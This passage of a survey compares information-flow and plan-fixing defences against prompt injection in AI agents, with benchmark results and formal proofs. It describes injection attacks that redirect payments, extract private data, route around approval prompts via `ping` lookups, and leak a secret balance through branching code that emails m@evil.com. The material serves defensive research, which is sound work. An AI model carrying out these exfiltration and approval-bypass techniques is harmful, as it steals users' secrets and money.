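Such an estimate would be hard to use against an attacker. Suppose an agent ignores nearly every web page but obeys one rare form of injection. On ordinary pages, its payments would carry almost no information on average about what it read, so the label would look safe. The estimate would have to cover the agent's behavior on the worst page, which an attacker may find first. Even a small amount of information can be decisive, since one bit is enough to determine whether a payment goes ahead.

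The paper suggests two other approaches. A system could remove or alter part of the input and measure the change in the agent's likely actions, much as CausalArmor does. Or researchers could trace information inside the model well enough to build a simpler program that represents it, and track labels through that program. All three are research directions, and the paper doesn't test them.

### Tracking single records in FlowSeal

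*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) introduces FlowSeal, which loosens only the confidentiality label. FlowSeal stores each private record along with its owner and permitted recipients. When the agent reads something, code compares the text with the stored records and adds any matches to a list. When the agent later tries to send or write something outside, code allows trusted destinations and blocks banned ones. For any other destination, it gives the listed records and the proposed text to a separate language model, which returns one word, "safe" or "blocked".

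In the café example, FlowSeal would list the rota after step 2. At step 4, the checker would compare the rota with the opening hours, find that the hours reveal nothing about it, and allow the post. A context label couldn't support this decision, because it records only that the agent has read something private, not whether the new text contains any of it.

Shim and colleagues designed FlowSeal to stop outsiders from persuading an agent to disclose private data. In one of their attacks, an outsider creates a page of true and false claims about someone's health and asks the agent to delete the false ones. The agent writes nothing confidential, but the outsider can infer that the remaining claims are true. On live Gmail and Notion accounts, this attack extracted 34.7% of the private items from an agent protected by an earlier defence and none from one protected by FlowSeal. Across all the tests,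 FlowSeal limited leaks to between 0% and 3.3% of items. The agent completed 72.4% of harmless tasks with FlowSeal, compared with 75.9% with the best of the other defences.

FlowSeal doesn't track integrity, so it would not stop the payment that was blocked in step 5. Shim and colleagues also exclude prompt injection from their threat model, but the checker reads the text the agent wants to send, so an injection could get the agent to include an instruction to answer "safe". The guarantee they prove holds only if the checker never wrongly answers "safe". FIDES is designed so that ordinary code tracks the labels and checks every call, so they are wrong to criticise it for leaving all enforcement to a language model. FlowSeal depends more than FIDES does on a model's judgement when data is released.

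### Human approval

A system can also ask a person to approve each call it would otherwise block. The café manager would see one request at step 4 and another at step 5, and could approve both in seconds. But Microsoft concedes that its approvals are coarse. The request shows the tool and the label that caused the block, but not how the label arose. Requests for a legitimate payment and an injected one would both list untrusted content as the reason, so the manager would have to notice a wrong account number or amount without help. Each approval also covers only the blocked call, so the context presumably stays untrusted and the next payment prompts another request.

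Neither the FIDES paper nor Microsoft's announcement reports how many approvals an agent needs, but the AgentDojo results allow a rough estimate. With GPT-4o and only a context label, switching on the policies reduced average task completion from 84% to 42%. If most of the lost tasks would have succeeded with a person approving the blocked calls, about four tasks in ten needed at least one approval, rising to about seven in ten in the Slack suite. With FIDES, average completion fell from 61% to 50%, which suggests that about one task in ten needed approval.

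The estimate for FIDES is probably too low, because GPT-4o failed many tasks before reaching a forbidden call, and a task may need several approvals. Still, the difference suggests hiding data could spare users many interruptions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cites later work that combines endorsement with planning around labels to reduce approval requests further, but gives no counts.

An operator can also reduce the number of approval requests by exempting actions that seem harmless, but each exempted action must actually be harmless. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, required approval for many commands that could send data to unknown domains, but not for `ping`, which tests whether another computer is reachable. An injection could make the agent read secret keys and put them into the address that `ping` looked up. The lookup would then send the keys to the attacker's server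 without an approval request.

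## Fixing the plan before reading untrusted data

In FIDES, the main model chooses each step after the previous one has run, so the system has to control what the model sees between steps. A stricter design has the model write the whole plan from the user's request before any tool runs, so an injection in a tool's output cannot add a step or change the order. This design also doesn't need to infer which input caused each call, as AgentArmor does, because every call in the plan comes from the user's request.

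### CaMeL

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) describes Google DeepMind's CaMeL, the best-known system of this kind. In CaMeL, a privileged model reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the program and calls the tools. When the program requires information from untrusted text, a quarantined model without tools extracts it, much as in FIDES. Before each tool call, a policy written as a short Python function checks the arguments and allows or refuses the call.

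The two models come from Willison's dual LLM pattern. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, credits the CaMeL paper with finding a flaw in his design. An injection can't change the steps, but it can make the quarantined model return the wrong email address, which the next step then uses. CaMeL's interpreter therefore attaches a record, called a capability, to each value, listing its sources and permitted readers. The permitted readers of a calendar event, for example, might be the user and the people invited.

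Willison illustrates CaMeL with a user who asks the agent to find Bob's address in the last email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting. In simplified form, the program is:

```
1  email = get_last_email()
2  address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's address", email)
3  send_email(recipient=address, body="Remember our meeting")
```

The interpreter builds the data-flow graph as it runs these lines:

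| Value | Computed from | Original source | Trusted |
|---|---|---|---|
| `email` | Result of the email tool | Whoever wrote the email | No |
| `address` | `email` | Whoever wrote the email | No |
| `body` | Text in the program | The user's request | Yes |

The interpreter passed `email` to the quarantined model and stored the answer in `address`, so no model has to judge where `address` came from. If the policy for `send_email` requires a trusted recipient, CaMeL blocks the call or asks the user to approve it.

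The graph records exactly which values the interpreter passed from one operation to the next, but not what happened inside the quarantined model. In the graph, the address depends on the whole email, whether the model copied it from Bob's signature or from a sentence that a stranger planted. Both addresses have the same dependencies, so a policy that blocks the planted one also blocks the real one.

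### Leaks through branches and retries

*The LLMbda Calculus* identifies two gaps in CaMeL's tracking. The first involves code that doesn't run. Suppose an account balance is secret and a program contains these lines:

```
1  rich = True
2  tmp = True
3  if balance > limit: tmp = False
4  if tmp: rich = False
5  if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the limit, line 3 changes `tmp`, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. Line 4 then skips its assignment, so CaMeL never marks `rich`, and line 5 sends the email. If the balance is lower, line 4 sets `rich` to false and no email goes out. The recipient therefore learns whether the balance is above the limit, even though CaMeL treats `rich` as public. AgentArmor's graphs similarly miss paths not taken.

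The second gap is that CaMeL doesn't track the ordinary Python loop that surrounds the interpreter and retries after a failure. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so repeated attempts could reveal the secret one bit at a time.

*The LLMbda Calculus* cites these gaps as reasons for a proof that covers the whole system. The gaps are probably hard for an outsider to exploit, because the privileged model writes the program without reading the outsider's text.

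### Why CaMeL's scores differ

The first version of the CaMeL paper, from March 2025, reports that CaMeL solved 67% of AgentDojo's tasks. The revised version from June reports 77%, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. CaMeL's 67% and 77% are both well above the 48% in the AgentArmor paper's comparison and the 48% to 53% that Wang, Li and Tian measured.

The choice of model probably explains part of the difference, because the privileged model has to write a correct program without seeing any results. It is unlikely to explain all of it, because undefended agents did almost as well in the tests by Wang, Li and Tian (73% and 79%) as in CaMeL's own tests.

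Another possible cause is the tool descriptions. An ordinary agent can look at a tool's output and work out its structure, but CaMeL has to write the code that handles the output before seeing it. AgentDojo's default descriptions don't specify what the tools return. According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to groups of agents, CaMeL's developers had to add this information for their tests. CaMeL would do much worse in a comparison without it, but Wang, Li and Tian don't say whether they added it.

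The policies can also make a large difference. On AgentDojo's banking suite, *The LLMbda Calculus* reports that switching them on halves CaMeL's utility. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, ran CaMeL with its policies on all 97 tasks, using Claude Haiku 4.5 and no injections. They ran their own extension of CaMeL on the same tasks, which helps separate bad plans from blocked ones:

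| Suite | Tasks | Completed by CaMeL | Plan failed under both systems | Other, mostly blocked by policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Slack | 21 | 6 | 5 | 10 |
| Banking | 16 | 6 | 2 | 8 |
| Travel | 20 | 9 | 10 | 1 |
| Workspace | 40 | 28 | 5 | 7 |
| Total | 97 | 49 | 22 | 26 |

CaMeL completed 51% of the tasks, close to the figures from Wang, Li and Tian. If all 26 tasks in the last column had succeeded without the policies, the total would have been 75, or 77%. This matches CaMeL's own revised figure, which may be a coincidence, but it shows that policies alone could produce a gap of this size. A better planner might help most with travel, where half the plans failed, and much less with banking, where policies caused most of the failures.

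In real use, the user could approve some of the blocked calls, but might do so without checking them. Willison worries that ordinary users will struggle to write and maintain the policies.

CaMeL is also expensive. Wang, Li and Tian measured about 81,000 tokens per task, roughly seven times as many as for an undefended agent.

### Checking the program before it runs

Once the plan is a program, ordinary code can look for problems in it before any tool runs. CaMeLoT, the extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, converts the program into a finite set of states and possible steps between them. It then uses a model checker, software that examines every path through such a system, to test rules like this one:

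AG(call_update_password ⇒ password_trusted)

AG means "at every point on every path", so the rule requires a trusted password wherever the plan changes the password. In this way, CaMeLoT can check 22 of the 28 security policies that CaMeL uses for AgentDojo. The other six depend on facts available only at run time.

CaMeLoT's rules can also require an action, so unlike AgentArmor, it can reject a plan that leaves out a required step. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven unsafe plans for an agent that handles security alerts, including one that never disconnects a compromised computer. CaMeLoT caught all seven, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The researchers chose most of the rules because CaMeL's policies can't express them, so the result reflects the kinds of rule each system supports, not overall security.

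### IPIGuard

*IPIGuard* (An, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) fixes the plan as a graph of tool calls instead of a program. The graph has an edge from one call to another if the second needs the first one's output. The model builds the graph from the user's request, the tool descriptions and trusted background information, and marks any arguments it can't fill in yet as unknown. The agent then makes the calls in order and fills in the unknown arguments from earlier results.

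IPIGuard doesn't use security labels, and the model that fills in the arguments reads the tools' outputs directly. Unlike CaMeL, it therefore doesn't have to decide how to handle an output before seeing it, but an injection can still reach a model that helps determine the next call.

Two additions make the fixed graph more useful and harder to manipulate. The first, node expansion, lets the agent add calls that only read information. In one example, a user asks the agent to collect employees' hobbies from Bob's Slack inbox and post them on the company website. The agent may open more messages or pages to find the hobbies, but if a message or page contains an instruction to send money, IPIGuard blocks the payment.

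The second addition deals with injections that use a tool already in the plan. Suppose the user wants to pay for an order, and the injection contains an instruction to pay someone else. IPIGuard prompts the model to put any instruction it finds into a new call instead of changing the planned one. IPIGuard then returns a simulated result without running the new call, so the model treats the instruction as finished and fills in the planned payment as the user intended. This depends on the model recognising the instruction as a separate task, which an attacker could try to prevent.

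An and colleagues tested both additions on AgentDojo with GPT-4o-mini. The attack presented the injection as an important instruction:

| Version | Utility without attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed graph only | 52.58% | 3.18% |
| With added read-only calls | 64.95% | 4.77% |
| With simulated results | 51.55% | 0.32% |
| With both | 69.07% | 0.64% |

The undefended agent completed 68.04% of tasks, and the same attack succeeded in 27.19% of cases. Elsewhere in the paper, IPIGuard's utility is 67.01%, a difference of two tasks. The fixed graph alone therefore stopped most attacks but lowered utility by about 15 percentage points, and the read-only calls restored nearly all of that loss. Under attack, IPIGuard used 14,605 input tokens and 13.88 seconds per task, both about twice the undefended agent's figures. These are good results for a modest overhead, but all four attacks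 in the study are standard ones that don't target IPIGuard's prompts.

Read-only calls can also leak data, because an agent can open a web address that contains it, as EchoLeak did with an image link. An and colleagues attribute the small rise in attack success to harmless behaviour, such as opening a website the attacker named, but these calls are less safe than they assume. An operator would need to restrict the addresses an agent can open as well as the tools it can use.

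### AuthGraph

AuthGraph only compares the agent's calls with a separate plan, so the agent can still choose its own steps and handle unexpected results. For each sensitive parameter, the plan can require that the value come from the user's own words, appear exactly in a named tool's output, or be something the agent derived from that output. The planner can also leave a parameter unrestricted.

In one of the paper's cases, the user asks the agent to star a repository on GitHub, and an injection makes it try to star the attacker's repository instead. The agent calls the expected tool, but the repository's name doesn't match the user's request, so AuthGraph blocks the call.

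AuthGraph's good results on AgentDojo with GPT-4o carried over to the other models that Wang, Li and Tian tested:

| Model | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, AuthGraph | Utility, undefended | Utility, AuthGraph |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 17% | 1% | 73% | 69% |
| Qwen 2.5 70B | 15% | 2% | 69% | 63% |
| DeepSeek R1 70B | 31% | 3% | 65% | 62% |

Utility fell more on AgentDyn's less predictable tasks, from 50% to 37% with GPT-4o-mini, while attack success fell from 52% to 2%.

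When code can't find a value in the tool output it should come from, a language model decides whether to allow the value. The prompt printed in the paper lets the model reject a value only if it can quote an instruction in that output to use it. Followed literally, this rule would allow the fake flight `EVIL-123` in the paper's main example, because the model is given only the flight results and the instruction is in the hotel listing. The parameter check still stopped many attacks in the tests, so the tested version may differ from the printed prompt.

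### SPA

CaMeL, IPIGuard and AuthGraph plan for a single request, but an agent with memory may use the results of one request in another. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice from Acme and save the details, then asks it on Tuesday to pay the invoice. If Tuesday's planner reads the stored details, an injection in them can change Tuesday's plan.

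SPA shows the planner only a description of each stored item, which includes its format, its purpose and the request that produced it. The invoice's text couldn't influence the purpose, because the planner wrote it before any tool ran. SPA retrieves the invoice itself only while running the new plan, and restores the labels the invoice had on Monday.

SPA also replaces Python with a small planning language. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) had recommended such a change because features of Python such as exceptions make it hard to predict how information will flow. SPA's language has only six kinds of step: retrieving a stored item, calling a tool, asking the quarantined model, displaying a result, branching and looping. Before the plan runs, code computes a label for each step:

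λ(step) = pc ⊔ λ(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ λ(xₙ)

Here *x*₁ to *x*ₙ are the step's inputs, and *pc* is the joined label of the request and any conditions that control whether the step runs. The check covers both branches of every condition. A variable created inside a branch can't affect anything outside that branch, which rules out the leak through `rich`.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano on AgentDojo's 97 tasks and 949 attack cases from a newer release. They also split each task into two to five requests to create a version called AgentDojo-MQ. The attack used knowledge of the agent's tools:

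| Version of SPA | Utility, one request | Attack success, one request | Utility, several requests | Attack success, several requests |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No label check | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| With label check | 29.0% | 0.0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |
| No label check, stored values visible to planner | – | – | 65.9% | 0.6% |

With single requests, the label check prevented the four attacks that had succeeded and reduced utility by 24 percentage points. It rejected about 53% of runs, usually because the plan passed an untrusted result to a tool that required trusted input. In the test with several requests, SPA had rejected the plan in two of the runs recorded as successes with the label check, so the benchmark probably misjudged them.

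The paper doesn't give results for an undefended agent with this model, so it isn't clear how many attacks the fixed plan stopped. The results also provide little evidence about attacks through memory. Attack success was only 0.6% even when later planners could read the stored values, and Girrens and Wang acknowledge that this attack barely tests the danger. The results do show that later plans can reuse stored values that are hidden from the planner. When an earlier request had stored the necessary item, the later plan retrieved it 95.4% of the time without the label check and 89.9% with it.

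An optional mode also protects the planner from poisoned tool descriptions. In this mode, the planner writes its own descriptions of the tools it needs, and a later step matches them to the installed tools. About three-quarters of runs failed at this matching step. Utility for single requests was 14.1% without the label check and 6.7% with it, so this protection is not yet practical.

### When the next step depends on the data

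A fixed plan can include a decision if the planner knows the possible actions. For example, a program can check the delay and either reschedule or confirm the airport pickup.

Planning in advance doesn't work if the data determines what the possible actions are. For example, a user might ask an agent to work through a to-do list. If every item were a bill, a program could loop over the list and pay each one. But the list might also include booking a dentist appointment or replying to a landlord, and the planner can't write those steps before reading it. The planner could let the program use any of the agent's tools, but then an attacker who could edit the list could choose any of them too.

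IPIGuard allows new calls that read information but not new actions, so it could read the list but not carry out an unexpected item. An and colleagues argue that users should avoid such requests because they expose the agent to attack, which is safe advice but would rule out a lot of useful work. Wang, Li and Tian estimate that about 40% of AgentDyn's tasks include an explicit instruction to rely on outside content, which may help explain why CaMeL scored zero there.

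AuthGraph can plan again with a fixed set of tools, but SPA never revises a plan, even after a failed check, because the feedback could carry an attacker's text to the planner.

### Changed values inside approved actions

Fixing the plan doesn't make the values in it correct. Suppose the attacker changes only the account number on the Acme invoice. The invoice contains no instruction, the user asked for the payment, and the plan has the right steps in the right order. The designs lead to these outcomes:

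| System | Genuine invoice | Invoice with changed account number |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, if the account must be trusted | Blocked, or user asked | Blocked, or user asked |
| IPIGuard | Paid | Paid to the attacker |
| AuthGraph, if the account may come from the invoice | Paid | Paid to the attacker |
| SPA, if payments require trusted input | Rejected | Rejected |

None of the systems can pay the genuine invoice and automatically reject the altered one. IPIGuard's simulated results don't help, because the altered invoice contains no instruction to redirect into a separate call.

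Wang, Li and Tian explain why this limit is fundamental for AuthGraph. Let π(*t*) be the part of a run *t* that AuthGraph's plan can restrict, namely the sequence of tools and the kind of source for each parameter. For the genuine run *g* and the attacked run *a*,

π(*g*) = π(*a*)

Any check that uses only π must therefore give both runs the same result. The paper excludes two of 60 AgentDyn samples from its results for this reason.

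As with the landlord's file, telling the two invoices apart requires independent evidence, such as an account number saved from an earlier payment. Even without it, the fixed plan limits what the attacker can do. The altered invoice can redirect the payment to Acme, but it can't make the agent forward the user's address book.

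## Typed languages and what can be proved

When a task's next step depends on what the agent reads, the agent can't fix its plan in advance, but it can write its program piece by piece, reading results in between. A programming language can limit what each piece may do. Language designers have long proved that every program their language accepts obeys certain rules. Two projects from 2026 extend such proofs to programs that call language models.

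"Type" has three meanings in this work. AgentArmor's types are security labels and conditions attached to the graph of one run. In a typed programming language, types limit how a program may use a value or which actions it may perform, and the language rejects programs that break these limits. A restricted data type limits the form of the answer a model may return after reading untrusted text, for instance to a number or to yes or no. Correct types do not guarantee that a model's answer is true or that a program's security labels are right.

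### Restricted data types

*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) splits an agent into a quarantined part that reads untrusted data and a privileged part that chooses actions. The quarantined part may pass on only values of types the developer has chosen for that application, such as integers, and never free text. If the developer allows no types, the design becomes ordinary privilege separation, so it can secure every task that ordinary separation can.

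It is hard to inject an instruction through an integer. A very large one could encode a sentence, but the privileged model would have to decode the sentence before following it. The attacker can still choose the number, so a bill for 80 euros might become one for 8,000.

A short list of permitted answers limits the damage further. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, the revised version of *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) describe a function that makes a value trusted only if it is one of *n* fixed values. Each use of the function should then carry at most log₂ *n* bits, as with the fixed answer forms in FIDES. They have not formally proved this bound for their function, and they point out that the function doesn't suit their banking tasks, which need account numbers and amounts.

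The form of a value also doesn't show who chose it. Santos-Grueiro tested this on 192 constructed cases in which an agent read text that an attacker could edit. Forcing the agent's calls into a fixed format stopped it from using malicious tools and let legitimate calls through. But the attacker's text still determined protected fields in every case, so every case ended in an unauthorised action. When the system also checked the source of each field, no case ended in one. The cases were built to contain this flaw, so the rates don't show how common it is.

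### Language-Based Agent Control

Zhou and colleagues implement their approach, Language-Based Agent Control, in a system called ELBA, which uses the programming language Haskell. The developer calls the function `agent` with a prompt, a list of permitted tools and the type of result required. The model writes a program, and ELBA checks it against that type before running it. If the check fails, the model receives the error message and tries again.

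Haskell suits this purpose because its types also record a program's effects, such as writing a file or contacting a server. An agent with the result type `Int` must return an integer and can't do anything else. If someone asks a calculator agent to delete the server's files and then compute a factorial, the model may write a program that does both. But the deletion gives the whole program a different type, so ELBA rejects it.

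Types can also restrict where data comes from. In one example, an agent compiles a bibliography that may contain only records from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The function that writes to the file accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, which the agent can get only by fetching them from DBLP. The agent can sort and filter the records but can't invent one. In a test of 100 tasks, none of ELBA's 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search. The type doesn't ensure that the papers are relevant.

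The same method works for files. The agent receives a token for one folder and can derive further tokens only for that folder's contents. Claude Code instead compares the text of a command with permission rules, which is more fragile. Zhou and colleagues cite a bug reported in March 2026, in which Claude Code checked only the first of several chained commands against its list of forbidden commands.

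### Subagents and the soundness proof

ELBA allows a program written by the model to call `agent`, so an agent can react to what it reads. The program might run a search, put the first result in a new prompt and have a subagent decide what to do next. The subagent works under its parent's restrictions, which the parent can tighten but not loosen.

ELBA controls information flow with LIO, an existing Haskell library. Each computation has a current label, which works much like the context label in FIDES. The types ensure that every tool call goes through LIO, but LIO checks the labels at run time. A parent agent can run a subagent in a separate computation and receive the result sealed, so the parent's label doesn't change unless it opens the result.

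In CaMeL and FIDES, the model that reads untrusted text has no tools. An ELBA subagent starts with its tools, but when it reads untrusted data, its privileges drop to those of the data's source. LIO then blocks any call that requires more privilege, so the subagent loses its sensitive tools but may keep harmless ones.

Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language enforces for all well-typed programs also holds for programs that contain agents. The proof starts with the most deeply nested agent and replaces each call to a model with an ordinary function that returns a program and checks its type. The result is an ordinary well-typed program with the same sequence of tool calls, so the language's existing guarantee applies. The model can be any function from prompts to programs, including one that an attacker controls. The theorem preserves only what the language and its libraries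 enforce, so it doesn't rule out a dangerous call that the developer's policy permits.

### ELBA on the Slack suite

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack suite. Without attacks, the systems completed these numbers of the 21 tasks:

| Model | ELBA, policies off | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies off | CaMeL, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
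| Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT-5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |

With policies on, ELBA completed 37 tasks across the four models, and CaMeL completed 20. The sample is small, and for at least one model the difference could be due to chance. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL because it calls the model again after reading data. Writing Haskell was hardly an obstacle, since retries after failed type checks took only 3.4% of the running time.

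Since all 105 standard attacks failed against both systems even with policies off, the informative test is the one in which a subagent receives the injection as its only instruction. Zhou and colleagues ran the 105 cases seven times for each model, or 735 runs:

| Model | Attack success, policies off | Attack success, policies on | Tasks completed, policies off | Tasks completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
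| Opus 4.7 | 42.2% | 0% | 71.2% | 47.8% |
| Opus 4.8 | 37.4% | 0% | 75.8% | 42.4% |
| GPT-5.4 | 15.5% | 0% | 75.9% | 46.0% |
| Sonnet 5 | 26.5% | 0% | 67.2% | 40.0% |

This is much stronger evidence than a score on the standard attacks, because the subagent obeys the attacker from the start. But it covers only five attack goals in one suite, and the policies stopped the agent from completing a further 23% to 33% of tasks. Zhou and colleagues suggest using such policies to decide which calls need a user's approval, which would let the agent complete some of those tasks.

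### Explicit and implicit flows

A program can reveal a secret without copying any part of it. Take this one, in which only the balance is secret:

```
1  balance = get_balance()
2  if balance > 500000:
3      send_email("m@evil.com", "Hello")
```

An explicit flow occurs when a program copies a secret or computes a value from it. This email contains none, because its address and text are both fixed. But the balance determines whether line 3 runs, which is an implicit flow. The recipient learns whether the balance is above 500,000, which is one bit. If an attacker could repeat the test with other thresholds, halving the range each time, 20 tests would be enough to find any whole-euro balance below a million, since 2²⁰ is 1,048,576.

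*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* describes FIDES's guarantee as safety (forbidden calls don't happen) plus explicit secrecy, which covers only explicit flows. Garby and colleagues object that the guarantee ignores secrets that escape through control flow. They add that it is weakest where data and control are interchangeable, which seems to describe an agent that turns text into actions. The FIDES researchers chose explicit secrecy deliberately and consider the guarantee sufficient against most practical injections.

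### Noninterference in the LLMbda calculus

LLMbda is a small formal language in which programs can prompt a model, copy or clear a conversation, and run code that the model writes. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation. The interpreter also keeps a program-counter label, which joins the labels of the conditions that led to the current instruction. In the example, this label becomes secret on line 3. If the email tool accepts only public input, the interpreter stops the run there.

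The conversation needs similar protection. Suppose a program adds a sentence to a public conversation only if a secret is true, and later asks the model about that sentence. If the interpreter labelled the conversation secret when the sentence was added, the conversation would still be public whenever the secret was false, so the label itself would reveal the secret. LLMbda therefore blocks the addition.

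Garby and colleagues prove termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. If two inputs differ only in parts that an observer is not allowed to see, the observer's results must have the same probabilities, apart from differences that unfinished runs could account for. The property is probabilistic because a model may answer the same prompt differently each time, and termination-insensitive because it allows secrets to affect whether a run finishes.

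Let P_x(q) be the probability that a run on input *x* finishes with visible result *q*. These probabilities may add up to less than 1, and the remainder is the probability that the run doesn't finish, including runs that the interpreter blocks. For any inputs *x* and *x′* that look the same to the observer, there must be a function ω such that

P_x(q) ≤ ω(q) and P_x′(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, with Σ_q ω(q) ≤ 1

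The smallest suitable ω takes the larger of the two probabilities for each result, so the condition is equivalent to

Σ_q max(P_x(q), P_x′(q)) ≤ 1

The first two rows below apply this to the balance example. The third is an invented case in which the model answers at random.

| Program | Results if balance is high | Results if balance is low | Sum | Condition met |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No flow control | Email: 1 | No email: 1 | 2 | No |
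| Email blocked by LLMbda | None, run blocked | No email: 1 | 1 | Yes |
| Model answers yes or no | Yes: 0.6, no: 0.3 | Yes: 0.5, no: 0.4 | 1 | Yes |

If every run finishes, the two sets of probabilities must be identical. Otherwise the visible results may differ, but on a scale from 0 to 1 the difference is at most the average probability of not finishing. That limit is 0.5 in the second row and 0.1 in the third.

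The guarantee does not cover leaks through early stopping. In the second row, an observer who can tell that the run stopped early learns that the balance is high. LLMbda runs the agent's retry loop inside the language, where the same rules apply, to stop repeated attempts from leaking more. CaMeL leaves this loop untracked.

Lean, a proof assistant, has checked the proofs. They cover every program in the language, including code that the model generates, and apply to the interpreter that actually calls the model.

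### The RANDORI agent

Endorsement, which makes untrusted data trusted, deliberately breaks noninterference for integrity. Garby and colleagues prove that it can't weaken the protection of secrets, whatever the attacker's input. Their test agent, RANDORI, needs endorsement to do useful work. Its planner decides what to endorse before the agent reads any untrusted data. RANDORI also first tests each plan on artificial data, so an error message from a failed attempt can't carry an attacker's text into the next attempt.

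On AgentDojo's banking suite with no attacks, RANDORI completed 75% of tasks using GPT-5.2, while CaMeL completed 66.7% with its policies off and 37.5% with them on. Using MiMo-v2.5, RANDORI completed 64.6%, while CaMeL completed 70.8% with policies off and 37.5% with them on. RANDORI's MiMo-v2.5 result fell to 54.2% without endorsement, which lets the planner make exceptions, so endorsement accounts for part of RANDORI's advantage over CaMeL with policies on.

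The injection succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs, both on the same task. The user had asked the agent to make a payment following the instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The planner had endorsed those contents, so the theorem did not protect against the false payment.

The number of failed attacks is less impressive than it looks, because in 97 of the 144 combinations of task and injection, the user's task gives the planner no reason to include the call the attacker needs. But when a task told CaMeL to follow a file's instructions precisely, its planner wrote a program with a branch for every tool, so the file's contents determined which tool ran. Two attacks succeeded this way with CaMeL's policies off.

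### Context-to-Execution Integrity

CXI, Santos-Grueiro's system, checks each call just before it takes effect and doesn't require the agent to write in a special language. A call must have three kinds of authority:

- Each protected field, such as a file path or recipient, needs a value approved for that field.
- Content that a tool will interpret, such as a code change or a shell command, needs approval for its exact effect.
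- The call itself needs a permission that covers when and how often it may happen.

The last requirement prevents text in a log file from causing an agent to repeat an approved action, even if every field in the repeated call is correct. CXI ties all three requirements to a manifest, a record of the exact action that includes the current state of the files and the policy version. If anything changes after approval, the manifest no longer matches and CXI rejects the call. An attacker therefore can't use approval for a code change in one repository to make the change in another.

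As in the 400 coding runs, Santos-Grueiro observed nothing unauthorised among the 204 calls that CXI allowed on AgentDojo. The models often proposed unauthorised values, and did so in 196 of 300 proposals in one adversarial test. Of the 169 coding runs that didn't safely complete the task, 73 produced output that CXI couldn't parse, 61 lacked approval for the effect, and 35 ran but failed at the task. On AgentDojo, agents safely completed the task in 199 of 720 runs, but this total combines six test conditions and doesn't measure CXI's own utility.

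A smaller test supports checking more than the source of each argument. CXI rejected all 20 constructed attacks, while an approximation of argument tracking alone rejected 12. Both allowed all six legitimate calls.

All these results depend on the policies. An audit of the policies for 24 tools produced 18 findings, half of them serious. They included content classed as ordinary data although the tool would act on it, and approvals that didn't specify which field they covered. Santos-Grueiro reports that none was still a blocker in the final policies, but other operators would have to do the same work for their own tools.

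### What each guarantee assumes

Each guarantee holds only if certain parts of the system are correct:

| System | What it guarantees | What must be correct | What it doesn't promise |
|---|---|---|---|
| Type-directed privilege separation | Untrusted free text doesn't reach the privileged model | The separation and the choice of types | That a returned value is true |
| FIDES | Calls obey the policies, and secrets don't escape through explicit flows | Labels, policies, tool descriptions and the developer's instructions | That the choice of calls reveals nothing |
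| ELBA | Generated programs obey the rules that the language and its libraries enforce | Haskell, the libraries, labels, policies and tools | That the agent completes the task |
| LLMbda | Noninterference, for secrets even with endorsement | Labels on sources and checks in tools | That endorsed data is safe, or that failure to finish reveals nothing |
| CXI | An accepted call has approval for its fields, effects and occurrence | Policies, approval code, tools and the record of influences, with no way around the check | That the action is useful, or that the model is free of untrusted influence |

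LLMbda's theorem also treats all data sources as part of the program. Garby and colleagues acknowledge that a better model would include tools and data outside the program. The proof would not cover a tool that secretly sends its input elsewhere.

None of these systems guarantees a truthful summary. Suppose a user asks for a summary of a product report, and an injection makes the model leave out a safety warning. The system may correctly label the summary untrusted and show it to the user, who is allowed to read untrusted text. This breaks no rule, but the user may still buy a dangerous product.

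### Why an inferred graph can't inherit these proofs

A proof of noninterference needs labels that account for every influence. If *u* influences *v*, then the label of *v* must be at least as restrictive:

u influences v ⇒ ℓ(u) ⊑ ℓ(v)

LLMbda's interpreter ensures this by rule, whatever the model returns. Code the model writes starts with the label of the whole conversation that produced it. LIO does much the same in ELBA by keeping one label for everything a computation has read. Neither system has to determine which sentence caused which action.

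AgentArmor's graph contains only the edges that its analyser reports. If the analyser misses an edge, the type checker may apply every rule correctly and still allow an injected payment. One could prove that AgentArmor enforces its rules, assuming the graph contains every influence, but an attacker would target that assumption.

High measured accuracy wouldn't amount to a proof. If the analyser missed a relevant edge in 1% of calls and its errors were independent, it would miss at least one in about 18% of runs with 20 such calls. An attacker could also look for text on which it fails more often, whereas a proof covers every text the attacker might write. AgentArmor's graph also couldn't supply the influence record that CXI needs. CXI rejects a call when the origin of a protected field is unknown, but a missing edge in the graph looks the same as no influence.

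AgentArmor could recover a sound label by linking each call to everything the model had read, but this would cause label creep. It could instead use its graph to choose which text to remove and have the model regenerate the call, much as RTBAS does. That would make missed edges less dangerous but wouldn't give full noninterference, because an attacker's text could still affect the analyser's choice of what to remove.
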